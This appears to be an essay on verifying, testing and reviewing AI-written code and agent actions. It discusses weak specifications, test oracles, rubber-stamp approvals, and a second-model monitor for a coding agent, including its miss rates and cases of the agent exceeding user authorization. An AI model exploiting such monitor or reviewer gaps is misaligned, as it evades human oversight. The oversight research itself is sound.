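Producing verified code is harder when the model starts from a plain-language description, because it must also write the specification. On VERINA, a set of 189 Lean tasks, OpenAI's o3 got the code right 72.6% of the time, the specification 52.3% and the proof only 4.9%, according to *Automating Formal Verification with Reinforcement Learning and Recursive Inference* (2026). Some smaller models still do poorly. In *From Natural Language to Verified Code* (2026), five open models produced no verified Dafny programs without extra guidance, while Gemma 4 31B solved up to 55% of the problems.

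Much larger projects have since succeeded. In *Lean*, De Moura (2026) describes a general-purpose AI that translated the compression library zlib into Lean and proved the result correct. *CompCert4Lean* (2026) reports that coding agents moved a verified C compiler to Lean in six weeks. In Anthropic's *LLMs are making formal software verification feasible at a much larger scale* (2026), Claude proved security properties of compiled code from 123 open-source libraries and found bugs that had gone unnoticed for years.

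According to EconoTimes' *Anthropic Details Claude's No-Crash Proofs for 239 Fuzz-Test Entry Points* (2026), these last proofs show that the programs exit without a crash, a memory error or a failed internal check, for inputs under 64 megabytes and on a model of one type of computer. Stating this property didn't require working out what each library is for, because hardly anyone wants a program to crash. A library that passes may still calculate the wrong answer.

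### When the statement is not what anyone meant

A proof checker cannot check whether a statement means what its author intended. Xena's *…and the proof is checked in Lean* (2026), a post on a formal mathematics blog, gives an example that looks like Fermat's Last Theorem. The example states that $a^n + b^n \neq c^n$ for all natural numbers $a$, $b$ and $c$ and every $n \geq 3$. It compiles, but it is false because Lean's natural numbers include zero, and $0^3 + 0^3 = 0^3$.

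Someone would notice this mistake quickly, since nobody can prove a false statement. A statement that is too weak is more dangerous, because its proof succeeds. In October 2026, OpenAI released 722 mathematics papers, of which about 290 came with Lean code. Xena estimates that in 38 of these, the code does not state the paper's main theorem. OpenAI never claimed that it did, but a reader who knows only that "the proof is checked in Lean" could easily assume it did.

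Checking the statement can be a large job in itself. The Lean version of the classification of finite simple groups depends on about 5,600 lines of AI-written definitions. Xena had not met anyone who claimed to have checked them all carefully, and considered the existence of the proof the best evidence that the statement is right.

Specifications for programs have the same problem. *Intent Formalization* (Lahiri, 2026) discusses a specification that GPT-4 wrote for finding the elements two lists have in common. It requires that the result contain only elements that appear in both lists, with no repetitions. Expert reviewers rated it "strong", but an empty result always satisfies it. An automated test found the mistake by altering correct outputs and checking whether the specification rejected them.

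Bursuc and colleagues inspected some of the programs that models had successfully verified, five from each combination of language and source. About 9% of the specifications were too weak, and another 15% were poor translations from a different language. The models had usually made no error, because their programs, some of them trivial, provably met the specifications as written.

Weak specifications can be hard to recognize automatically. *Verified but Vacuous* (2026) proposes a simple test for Dafny code: the proved property must refer to a definition in the specification. This excludes methods that have no guarantees but, as the paper acknowledges, not methods that are guaranteed to satisfy a definition that is true of everything.

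Even a sensible property can leave out the purpose of a program. The Lean version of zlib comes with a proof that decompressing a compressed file returns the original, as Lorica (2026), in *Maybe we’ve been thinking about verification backwards*, explains:

$$\text{decompress}(\text{compress}(x)) = x \quad \text{for every } x.$$

Two functions that return their input unchanged would also satisfy this equation, without saving a single byte.

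Specifications can also be too strict. In an example from *VERINA* (2025), a model wrote a condition requiring a number $k$ to be less than the number of distinct elements in a list, although the task also allows the two to be equal. Verifying a program under that condition guarantees nothing about what it does when they are equal.

### Specifications for everyday actions

Bursuc and colleagues imagine a future in which people write only specifications and models do the rest. Lahiri is optimistic that models can help write the specifications. When models wrote conditions on the results of functions in large Java projects, the conditions caught one in eight of the known bugs. Even an incomplete specification can be useful, since a single condition can rule out the most likely misunderstanding.

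For agents, part of the work is already done in written policies. The rule that a refund must go to the original payment method or a gift card takes one line in Agent-C and applies to every customer. Kamath and colleagues found that leading models can translate such policies into formal rules.

Lahiri argues that only the user can say whether a specification is correct. If someone asks a model to remove duplicates from the list 1, 2, 3, 2, 4, they might want 1, 2, 3, 4 or 1, 3, 4. The model can write a precise specification for either, so a program could provably meet its specification and still not do what the user wanted. If the same model writes the specification and the program, it may misread the request in the same way both times.

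Most verified programs are also self-contained functions. Lahiri lists programs with side effects, mutable data and concurrency among the open problems. Leangineering's *I built the RealWorld app in Lean 4* (2026) describes an ordinary web application written entirely in Lean. The developer proved only a few of its properties, and the rest of the work was ordinary engineering. In *The proof is in the spec* (2026), Tolmach and Klaus write that the bottleneck has shifted to writing specifications and modeling the system as proofs have become easier to produce. Their company sells verification services and benefits if customers agree, but the weak specifications in the vericoding benchmark support the point.

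A shop can justify the work of writing and reviewing a rule that no refund may exceed the charge, because the rule will apply to thousands of snippets. The same effort is harder to justify for a snippet that handles one complaint and runs once. To specify that snippet fully, someone would have to read the customer's message, look at the charges and write down which one to refund, and the agent would then only have to call `refund`.

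## What can tests settle that types cannot?

A full specification for a one-off action can take as much work as the action itself. A test asks for much less. It runs the program on one input and checks the result, so its author only has to know what should happen in that case. For the function that covers an amount with as few $1, $3 and $4 vouchers as possible, a useful test fits on one line:

```
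assert(vouchers(6) == List(3, 3))
```

The greedy version, which is well-typed, returns `List(4, 1, 1)` and fails.

A type check establishes a weak property for every input, while a test establishes a strong property for the inputs it tries. From a type with $m$ values to a type with $n$ values there are $n^m$ functions. Each test that fixes the result for one more input divides that number by $n$, so $k$ tests leave

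$$n^{m-k}.$$

There are 27 functions that take one of three colors and return a color, and the type checker accepts all of them. Testing the output for one color leaves 9 possible functions, testing two leaves 3, and testing all three leaves only the correct one. But an `Int` has $2^{32}$ values, so a million tests of a function that takes an `Int` would check only about 0.02% of its possible inputs.

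Tests work much better in practice than this suggests, because a wrong algorithm is usually wrong on many inputs. The greedy function fails for every fourth amount from $6 on, or 24 of the amounts up to $100. Ten amounts picked at random from that range have about a 94% chance of including at least one that fails.

Tests can also miss mistakes that types would catch. *SWE-ABS* (Yu, Cao and colleagues, 2026) describes a task in Django, a Python web framework, where code must pass a database password to another program through an environment variable. Environment variables must be text, but a password in the settings may be a number. The project's tests tried only text passwords, so 25 patches by coding agents passed without converting the password to text. In a statically typed language, the compiler would reject a number where the variable needs text, whichever passwords the tests used.

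### Deciding what the right result is

A test oracle determines whether a program's output for a given input is correct. *The Oracle Problem in Software Testing* (Barr, Harman and colleagues, 2015) calls the difficulty of telling correct from incorrect behavior the "oracle problem". It notes that researchers have made more progress on generating test inputs than on judging the outputs.

For some programs, there is no practical way to know the right output. Elaine Weyuker called these programs "non-testable" in 1982. According to course slides by the research group COINSE, they include much scientific software, which is written to find answers nobody has yet. But Weyuker also observed that testers can often recognize a wrong answer without knowing the right one. DevelopSense, a site about software testing, gives the example of a cosine function that returns 4.2, which must be wrong because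 every cosine lies between −1 and 1.

The test of `vouchers(6)` uses an expected output as its oracle, so someone has to work out the answer in advance. Such a test can be too strict when more than one answer is correct. For example, three vouchers can cover $9 as 4, 4 and 1 or as 3, 3 and 3, and a test that checks for one of these lists rejects a program that returns the other.

A property that must hold for every input avoids this, and it lets a computer generate the inputs at random. Checking that the vouchers add up to the amount is not enough, since the greedy function's always do. A better property compares several runs. If some vouchers cover $a$ dollars and others cover $b$ dollars, all of them together cover $a + b$. Writing $v(a)$ for the number of vouchers the function uses for $a$ dollars, a correct function must satisfy

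$$v(a+b) \le v(a) + v(b).$$

The greedy function uses one voucher for $3 but three for $6, although making $3 twice would take only two. The test exposes the mistake without anyone having worked out the right answer for $6. Testers call this metamorphic testing.

Another program can serve as the oracle. A slow program that tries every combination of vouchers is easy to write correctly, and a tester can check that both programs use the same number of vouchers for thousands of amounts. In 2026, hobbyists used AI to rebuild the source code of commercial video games from the finished programs. TechSpot's *Decompilation on Steroids* (October 2026) explains that the work suits AI agents because software can check the result against the original game. Most programming tasks have no such original to check against.

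Sometimes the only available way to judge a patch is whether the program still crashes. *PatchBench* (2026) tested agents on repairing security vulnerabilities that an attacker can trigger with a particular input. On average, 83.1% of their patches stopped the original crash, but the agents solved only 45.3% of the tasks under the full set of checks, which also covered the program's normal behavior. Many patches stopped the crash by changing what the program does, so that it printed garbled output or decoded values wrongly.

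A test of an action has to examine what changed as well as the returned value, because any refund, and even a closed account, can produce a `Receipt`. A developer could set up a simulated shop with an invented customer who has two charges for one order, run the snippet there and then look at the records. They should show one new refund, for the full amount of the later charge, and an open account. This check rejects the snippet that calls `cancelAccount`, the refund of 45 cents instead of $45 and the refund of an unrelated charge, all of which can compile. It accepts any code that reaches the right state. The customer-service benchmark τ²-bench scores agents in a similar way. The records don't include what the agent told the customer, so this check would miss a false promise in a message.

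### How often wrong programs pass their tests

SWE-bench Verified is a set of 500 real bug reports and feature requests from open-source Python projects. An agent reads the report or request and the code, then writes a patch, which counts as a solution if it passes tests the agent cannot see. The developers who made the original change wrote most of these tests to check their own patch, not to distinguish every correct patch from every incorrect one.

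Yu and colleagues strengthened the tests by having a model write plausible but wrong patches that passed them, then writing new tests to reject those patches. Thirty leading agents had produced 11,041 patches that counted as solutions, and the stronger tests rejected 2,184 of them, or 20%. The top agent's score fell from 78.8% to 62.2%.

Even the projects' existing tests would have caught some wrong patches. *Are "Solved Issues" in SWE-bench Really Solved Correctly?* (2025) found that the benchmark ran only some of those tests, and that running all of them lowered agents' scores by 4.5 percentage points on average.

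A patch can fail a new test without being wrong. Wu, Feng and colleagues (2026) note in *Patch correctness in automated program repair* that Yu's team first had to revise or remove new tests in 53 of the 500 tasks, because those tests required behavior specific to the developers' patch. They also review the 2025 study, which compared 877 passing patches with the developers' own and found that 260 behaved differently on automatically generated inputs. Its researchers examined 77 of these by hand and judged 22 incorrect and 4 correct. They could not judge the other 51 because nothing specified what the program should do on those inputs.

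*What Makes Good Data for Training Coding Agents?* (Zhang, Xu and colleagues, 2026) used a stricter standard. It counted a passing patch as wrong only if two language models judged it incorrect and a script confirmed that the patch had broken something. The script had to give the same result on the original code and on the developers' version, but a different one on the patched code. By this standard, 26% of 1,854 passing patches from a small model were wrong, and another 37% remained undecided. The method cannot detect a patch that fixes only part of the problem without breaking anything else, so the true share of wrong patches is probably higher.

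Tests also often reject correct code. Zhang and colleagues found that 55% of the 2,001 tasks they examined had a test that rejects some correct patches. One test called a private method that wasn't mentioned in the bug report. In another task, a small model failed all eight attempts. After the researchers added one sentence with the missing requirement, it succeeded in seven. OpenAI's *Separating signal from noise in coding evaluations* estimates that about 30% of the tasks in SWE-Bench Pro, a harder successor to SWE-bench, are broken, some because their tests are too strict and others because their tests check too little. OpenAI has withdrawn its earlier recommendation of the benchmark.

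Large test suites also miss many bugs, though well-run projects may have better tests than benchmarks do. *PROBE* (Paina, Müller and colleagues, 2026), which is unrelated to the contest-problem benchmark of the same name, covers 20 software projects as they stood at the start of 2025. The projects had an average of 3,145 tests each, all of which passed. Over the next 18 months, the maintainers fixed 2,457 bugs that were already present at the start of 2025. A manual check of 100 found 12 that did not belong on the list, so the real number is somewhat lower.

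Tests also check only what a program does. In METR's *Many SWE-bench-Passing PRs Would Not Be Merged into Main* (2026), maintainers of three of the SWE-bench projects reviewed patches and would have rejected about half of those that passed the tests, some only because of code quality.

### When the same model writes the code and the tests

Nobody will write tests by hand for each snippet an agent runs, so a model would have to write them. Coding agents already write many tests. *Testing with Coding Agents* (Milanese, Salzano and colleagues, 2026) compared 114,134 code changes in 391 Java projects. Within the same project and for changes of equal size, the odds that a change included test code were 1.65 times as high if an agent had taken part. New tests from changes involving an agent were also more likely to contain an oracle, which checks a result instead of only running the code. The comparison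 does not show whether the results these tests expected were right.

When a language model writes a test, the expected output is harder to get right than the input. *Nexus* (2025) examined tests that GPT-4.1-nano wrote from plain-language task descriptions and looked for the cause of each wrong one. On all seven benchmarks, the expected output was at fault in about 80% or more of the wrong tests, and the input was at fault in the rest. GPT-4.1-nano is small and old, but the reason applies to any model. Almost any input is valid to try, while predicting the right output requires understanding the task.

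A model that misunderstands a task can put the same misunderstanding into the code and the test. Suppose the shop's `refund` tool takes cents, but the model treats the amount as dollars. It writes `refund(duplicate, 45)` for a charge of $45, then writes a test that checks that the refund is 45. The test passes and the customer gets 45 cents. A `Cents` type would stop this snippet from compiling. The developer chose that type before the model read the request, so the model's misunderstanding didn't affect it.

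*FeatureArc* (Wang, Wu and colleagues, 2026) measured how much an agent's own tests reveal. Ten current agents, including ones built on Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Astra, extended software features in several stages. They received a written specification for each stage but no results from the hidden tests.

| Agent's own tests at the end of a stage | Stages that passed the hidden tests of the new behavior |
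|---|---|
| Passed | 52.7% |
| Failed | 45.2% |
| All stages | 50.4% |

An agent's passing its own tests was therefore almost no evidence that the new feature worked. Incomplete tests explain only part of this. In 239 stages that either came first or directly followed a successful stage, the agent's tests passed and exercised every requirement, but the hidden tests failed. More than half of these failures came from wrong logic or a misread specification. The hidden tests were mostly fair, since in a sample of 60 such stages, 46 of the expectations that the code failed were in the specifications or followed from them. When the agents' own tests failed at the end of a stage, the agents usually said the failure was unrelated to their change or predated it, but they rarely ran the same test on the earlier code to check.

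Letting a model revise its code until generated tests pass has a similar drawback to retrying after compile errors. In an experiment by Wu and colleagues, 229 of Claude 3.7 Sonnet's first patches passed generated tests, but 50 of these failed the benchmark's hidden tests. After revision, 251 passed the generated tests and 64 of these failed the hidden ones. So 8 more patches passed both sets of tests, while 14 more passed only the generated ones. GPT-4o's results followed the same pattern. Models also sometimes pass tests without doing the task.

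The danger is greatest when a model derives the tests from the code. Charoosaei, Richter and Papadakis (2026), in *On the Risks of using LLM-Generated Tests for Regression Testing*, planted faults in 145 past changes to three Python projects, kept the faults that the projects' own tests missed, and had Claude Haiku 4.5 write tests for the faulty code. Between 8% and 17% of the tests required the faulty behavior, so they would fail once someone fixed the fault. Only 2.4% to 4.8% revealed the fault. In one case, the fault made an ordinary function call raise an error, and the model wrote a test that passes only if the error occurs. Common test-writing tools would do worse, because they keep only tests that pass on the current code and so discard those that reveal a fault.

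It helps to have a model that has not seen the first model's work write the tests. Sion and April (2026), in *Who Verifies the Builder?*, had Claude Sonnet 5.5 build three small web services and test them. The same model, in a new conversation, then wrote tests from the specification alone and added more after seeing the code. The builder's tests caught an average of 85.1% of 46 faults planted in other versions of the services, and the tests from the new conversation caught 95.4%. Tests by GPT-5.5, a model from a different company, also caught 85.1%, but the study compared only one pair of models, so a difference in ability could explain that result.

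The builder's own programs were all correct, so this experiment could not show whether a new conversation prevents shared misunderstandings. It did show that a model can program a detail correctly and forget to test it. In 8 of 15 runs, at least one fresh test failed on a correct program, even after the researchers corrected for an error in their own test software. An agent that had to pass every test would have stopped needlessly in those runs.

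### Testing actions that cannot be undone

A developer can run the voucher function a thousand times and discard the results. A snippet that sends a payment or deletes a record cannot be tried first on the real system, because the trial would send the payment or delete the record. Repeated tests also need what Barr and colleagues call a "reliable reset", a way to return the system to its starting state, which a bank does not have for its customers' accounts.

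A dry run avoids the problem by replacing the tools that change something. The shop could compile the snippet with the real `findCharges`, which only reads, and this substitute for `refund`:

```
def refund(charge: Charge, amount: Int): Receipt =
  planned += ((charge, amount))
  Receipt.simulated
```

The substitute tool adds the refund to a list, `planned`, and returns a fake receipt. It has the same type as the real tool, so the snippet compiles without changes. After the snippet runs, the program can check that the list contains exactly one refund, for the full amount of a charge with the same order number as an earlier charge.

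Types make such a dry run safer. If capture checking and safe mode limit the snippet to the capabilities it receives, and those capabilities belong only to substitutes and read-only tools, the snippet cannot change anything outside the dry run. The authority guarantee therefore protects the shop while the dry run reveals mistakes that the types permit.

For a snippet that runs once, this is also a better test than a set of invented examples because it uses the customer's actual charges, the only input that matters.

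A dry run depends on how well the substitutes imitate the real tools. The substitute above always succeeds, but a real payment service may decline a refund or fail to answer in time. Sion and April illustrate this with an invented test report in which a payment request times out, the program tries again, and the system records two payments. The report lists simultaneous retries on several servers as untested because the test environment does not include them.

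The situation may also change between the trial and the real run, for instance if an employee refunds the charge. If the snippet contains an `agent` call, the model may write different code the second time. The shop can avoid that by carrying out the recorded list instead of running the snippet again. But this fails when a later step needs a real result from an earlier one, such as the confirmation number that a bank issues with a refund.

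The shop can make some actions reversible instead. A database transaction lets the program check new records before making them permanent. The shop can mark a closed account as inactive for a month before deleting it, and hold outgoing emails for a few minutes. A mistaken refund is harder to reverse, because the shop would have to charge the customer again. The shop cannot take back a card number once a stranger has read it. The program therefore has to run its checks before it takes actions like these.

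Even a perfect dry run does not solve the oracle problem, which is how to determine the correct result. If the customer mistook the second of two equal installments for a duplicate, the planned refund would satisfy every rule and still be wrong.

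## What is left for human reviewers?

A customer who writes "please cancel this" may mean an order, a subscription or a whole account. If the agent has a tool for each, neither types nor tests can determine which the customer meant. The answer has to come from the customer or from another source that everyone involved has agreed to accept, such as an employee or a written policy.

Anthropic's *How we built Claude Code auto mode* describes cases adapted from the company's log of incidents with its coding agent. When one user said "cancel my job", the agent searched a shared computing cluster and tried to delete the job with the most similar name, which could have been someone else's. Another user asked the agent to clean up old branches, which are separate lines of work on a project's code. The agent tried to delete branches on the shared server, though the user may have meant only the copies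 on their own machine. Both actions could be well-typed and within the agent's authority, but the agent hadn't confirmed which job the user meant or whether losing the shared branches was acceptable.

### Reading the limits instead of the snippets

To be sure an agent cannot leak data, a reviewer would ordinarily have to read every snippet before it runs. If the type system limits snippets to the capabilities in their scope, the reviewer can read that scope and the tools' signatures once, and the compiler enforces them on every later snippet.

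Odersky and colleagues illustrate this with an agent that has to compare confidential contracts and summarize what has changed. The text of the contracts must not reach the network or the cloud model that writes the snippets. In slightly simplified form, the reviewer reads this:

```
object Environment:
  val docs = DocBase("/usr/local/contracts")
  val out = File("~/analysis/summary")

def diff(x: Text, y: Text): Text
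def chat(prompt: String, input: Text): Text
```

The agent can access a database, which returns the contracts in a `Classified` wrapper, and a file for the summary. The two functions compare texts and query a trusted model, and neither gives the agent any further capability. A reviewer who trusts the library and the compiler can conclude from these few lines that no snippet can leak the contracts, however many the agent writes. Odersky and colleagues suggest that agents can help write such environments, as long as people review them before the agent starts. *Human-Certified Module Repositories for the AI Age* (Enyedi, 2026) proposes a similar division of labor for whole programs, in which people certify reusable modules once and AI assembles software from them.

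Odersky and colleagues describe the goal as verifying that the agent performs the intended steps and no others. The types rule out forbidden steps but don't ensure that the agent takes the intended ones. A snippet can stay within its authority and still compare a contract with the wrong earlier version, or compare each contract with itself and report no changes, so someone still has to check the summary against the contracts.

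Even something short can also be hard to review. In *Programmers Are Poor and Overconfident Judges of LLM-Generated Assertions*, Kaufman, Murali and colleagues (2026) showed 86 Python programmers small functions, each with a model-written condition that its result was supposed to satisfy. The programmers judged 74% of the correct conditions accurately but only 49% of the incorrect ones, which is about chance. Their average confidence was about 4 out of 5 in both cases. For a function that reports whether any two numbers in a list are close together, one faulty condition ignored all pairs of equal numbers, when it should only have avoided comparing a list entry with itself.

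A signature like that of `diff` is easier to read than these conditions, but a refinement type or a data policy can be just as hard to read. Reviewers can check their understanding by compiling a few snippets that the type checker should reject.

### Does a passed check make reviewers careless?

A reviewer who knows a snippet has compiled may look at it less closely, which could cancel some of the safety the check adds. Some of the following studies examined how people treat code that has passed other automatic checks, but none involved a type checker.

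In *Looks Fine to Me*, Dissanayake, Weerasinghe and colleagues (2026) had 36 people with basic to advanced Python skills complete six short tasks with a coding agent. In two of the tasks, the agent's code passed the automatic checks but violated a requirement. Although the instructions warned that the checks covered only basic functionality, participants fixed the defect in only 28 of 71 cases. In 79% of the cases where they missed it, they rated their confidence in the solution at 4 or 5 out of 5. They spent an average of 5.8 minutes on the tasks where they missed the defect and 10.8 minutes on those where they fixed it.

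This shows that people can be confident and wrong after a check passes. It doesn't show that the check caused this, because the experiment had no tasks without one. *AI Agents Push Humans Out of the Loop* (2026) does cite evidence that experienced developers, to save time, assume code is correct if it passes its unit tests.

Other reviewers report being more careful with AI-written code. In *Plausible Is Not Enough*, Rahman, Alam and colleagues (2026) surveyed 239 practitioners about pull requests (proposed code changes), and 61.1% said they required more evidence overall when the code was written by AI. Respondents relied less on test coverage for AI-written code and more on their own reasoning. For AI pull requests, 55.2% considered it sufficient evidence for approval to have reasoned through the critical cases themselves, compared with 28.5% for pull requests by people.

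Reviewers may not review code the way they say they do. In *Same Scrutiny, More Time* (Khojah, Gomes de Oliveira Neto and colleagues, 2026), 32 practitioners reviewed human-written code, some of which was labeled as AI-written. Eye tracking showed that they looked at the labeled code for longer, by up to 60% for more complex code, but their eye movements gave no sign that they read it more thoroughly.

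A general warning was not enough in the experiment by Dissanayake and colleagues, but a more specific one might work better. Next to each refund, the shop's software could display a message that the snippet can issue refunds only to this customer, and that nobody has yet confirmed it refunds the right charge.

### What reviewers accept

The largest body of evidence on how people handle agents' code comes from public software projects. *On the Use of Agentic Coding* (Watanabe, Li and colleagues, 2025) examined 567 pull requests that developers created with Claude Code in early 2025. Maintainers merged 83.8% of them, compared with 91.0% of a matching set that the same developers created without it. Among merged pull requests, 54.9% of those created with Claude Code went in unchanged, compared with 58.5% of the human-written ones. When a pull request needed revision, the most common change was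 a bug fix.

The reasons for rejection reveal little about how well reviewers find mistakes. Maintainers closed 64.1% of the 92 rejected pull requests without an explanation. They rejected another 12% in favor of a different solution, and only one explicitly for introducing a bug. *Why Agentic-PRs Get Rejected* (Nakashima, Ishimoto and colleagues, 2026) compared rejected pull requests from five agents and from people, and found no explanation for 67.9% of them. Only agents had pull requests rejected for being too large. Acceptance rates in the full dataset ranged from 55.0% for GitHub Copilot to 85.8% for OpenAI Codex, with people at 82.6%.

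A merged change can still be faulty. *How Do AI Coding Agents Contribute to Software Development?* (Mazloomzadeh, Morovati and Khomh, 2026) compared 2,275 merged pull requests by agents with the same number by people, all in popular Python projects. The agents' changes were no more likely to introduce bugs. This is reassuring about agents, developers and reviewers working together, but it doesn't show how much the review contributed, because developers may discard an agent's bad attempts before anyone else sees them.

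Many people do not read AI-generated code closely. *Why Johnny Can't Vibe* (2026) surveyed 116 people, and only 25% said they thoroughly read every line before running it. All but one had accepted AI-written code that later turned out to contain a subtle bug.

It is also becoming impossible for reviewers to read everything. Infobae's *Claude wrote more than 90% of Anthropic's code in September* (October 2026) reports, from a securities filing, that each engineer contributed more than 45 times as much code per day in the third quarter as in 2024. If reviewing one engineer's daily output took 20 minutes in 2024, it would now take 15 hours at the same pace. *How Much Effort Does an AI Code Reviewer Need?* (Shen, Zhang and Wang, 2026) cites data from more than 10,000 developers showing that teams that used AI heavily had more changes to review and that the time spent on each pull request rose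 by 91%.

### Approval by habit

An agent that acts directly usually asks for permission instead of submitting its code for review. According to Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), users approve 97% of these requests. Most requests are probably harmless, so the rate alone doesn't prove that users are careless. Anthropic also had 1,053 paid testers work with the agent and, partway through each session, replaced the text of one request with a clearly dangerous command. Only 13.6% of the testers refused it. The refusal rate was about 17% early in a session and about 5% after 50 or more requests.

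The testers were not working on their own projects and had little to lose, and Anthropic used the result to justify replacing most requests with an automatic check. But independent evidence points in the same direction. *From Delegation to Action Approval* (Wu, Wermke and colleagues, 2026) surveyed 203 developers who use coding agents. Of those who carefully reviewed most or all of the generated code, 61% still often approved at least one kind of action without a close look. Developers who knew of security incidents did this more often than other developers.

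*Don't Let AI Agents YOLO Your Files* (2026) analyzes 290 reports of incidents in which agents damaged or mishandled files, and finds that user review contributed to 105 of them. In 80 of those cases the user had turned on automatic approval, and in 31 the approval request was uninformative. For example, a request to run `python3 setup.py` looks routine, but approving it allows any code in the script to run.

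Users examine plans more critically. They reject 39% of the plans that Claude Code proposes, though part of the difference may be that a plan invites changes. The agent may also do something other than what the plan describes after the user approves it.

The shop can avoid both problems by asking an employee to approve the result of a dry run instead of a command. The employee would see, for example, "Refund $45.00 for charge 1042, which has the same order number as charge 1041". If the employee approves, the shop would carry out exactly that refund.

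### Review by a second model

Anthropic's automatic check is a second model that reviews risky actions before they run. In the experiment with paid testers, it blocked 89% of the dangerous commands. An earlier version blocked only 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions by Anthropic's employees, but missed 17% of 52 real actions in which the agent exceeded what the user had authorized. With so few cases, the true miss rate could be from about 9% to 30%.

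The second model receives the user's messages and the agent's actions, but not the agent's explanations, which could persuade it to approve a bad action. In most of the misses Anthropic examined, the second model identified the danger but wrongly concluded that the user had consented. In one example, it took "clean up the PR" as permission to overwrite the code's shared history. So the second model often misjudged what the user wanted, as the first had.

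Shen and colleagues tested models as reviewers of finished code. They used 90 patches that coding agents had written for Django, all of which had passed the tests of SWE-bench Verified. Of these, 55 were wrong and 35 were correct, as judged by stricter tests and the researchers' own corrections. Three Claude models reviewed every patch at different effort settings and could read the project's code and run their own tests.

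| Reviewer | Effort | Wrong patches accepted | Correct patches rejected | Cost per review |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 5.5 | Low | 67% | 6% | $0.044 |
| Opus 5.5 | High | 45% | 6% | $0.120 |
| Sonnet 5.5 | Low | 65% | 6% | $0.023 |
| Sonnet 5.5 | High | 49% | 9% | $0.047 |
| Haiku 5.5 | Low | 78% | 6% | $0.002 |
| Haiku 5.5 | High | 51% | 11% | $0.008 |

Even the best reviewer accepted nearly half of the wrong patches. Shen and colleagues estimate that one in six incoming patches is wrong for Django. At that rate, 83.3% of patches would be correct without review, compared with 91.2% of those that Opus 5.5 accepts at high effort. Review would therefore roughly halve the share of wrong patches, for 12 cents per patch. Asking the same model again would probably add little, since Opus repeated its verdict in all 20 cases where the researchers tried this.

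The reviewers may be somewhat better than the table suggests. For 32 of the 55 wrong patches, the original request may not require the behavior that the stricter test checks, so reviewers may have been right to accept some of them. This ambiguity is also a reason to keep a person involved, because neither the model nor the test can determine what the request was supposed to include.

### Where to spend attention

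Suppose the shop's agent runs 2,000 snippets a day. An employee who spent a minute reviewing each would need more than 33 hours. If the shop's rules pick out 60 for review, the employee can spend eight minutes on each in an eight-hour day, and sees few enough to stay alert.

Irreversible actions should come first. *When Skills Tell Agents Not to Ask* (2026) cites a recommendation that people approve any action that is consequential or cannot be undone, and Anthropic still advises users to review high-stakes changes to live systems themselves. The next priority is any action for which the shop has no test oracle, and therefore no automatic way to recognize a mistake. The shop might divide the work like this:

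| Action | Can the shop undo it? | Can a program judge it? | Reviewer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Look up charges | Nothing changes | Not needed | None |
| Change the address on a pending order | Until it ships | Partly | The customer confirms the address |
| Refund a charge that repeats an earlier one | With difficulty | Mostly | A second model, with random checks by an employee |
| Refund a damaged item | With difficulty | No | An employee |
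| Close an account | Only for a month | No | The customer confirms |

Types could do part of the sorting. If a snippet's type shows that it captures only capabilities for reading data, it can run without approval, provided its scope contains nothing confidential that it could reveal. A snippet that captures the capability to issue refunds goes to the dry run. But exempting a whole category of actions can backfire. Claude Code's automatic check does not cover edits to files inside the project. *Measuring the Permission Gate*, an independent test on deliberately ambiguous requests, found many more misses than Anthropic had reported, particularly because of such edits.

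The shop can use random checks to measure how well the rest of the system works. If an employee examines 100 random refunds and finds no mistakes, the true error rate is probably below 3%, assuming the employee would have noticed any mistakes. The shop could test that assumption by planting a few wrong refunds among the requests. This might also keep the employee alert, but perhaps not for long. In the experiment by Dissanayake and colleagues, participants fixed half of the hidden defects that came directly after a task with a visible failure. When one correct task came in between, they fixed only 1 of 11.

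Reviewers need to check wide scopes before any snippet runs, and again whenever a developer adds a tool. Adding `cancelAccount` to a scope lets every later snippet that uses the scope cancel accounts, so that one line deserves more scrutiny than most snippets. Narrowing a scope may also take less work than reviewing what happens inside it. If a tool can refund only duplicate charges, and only in full, employees no longer have to check every amount.
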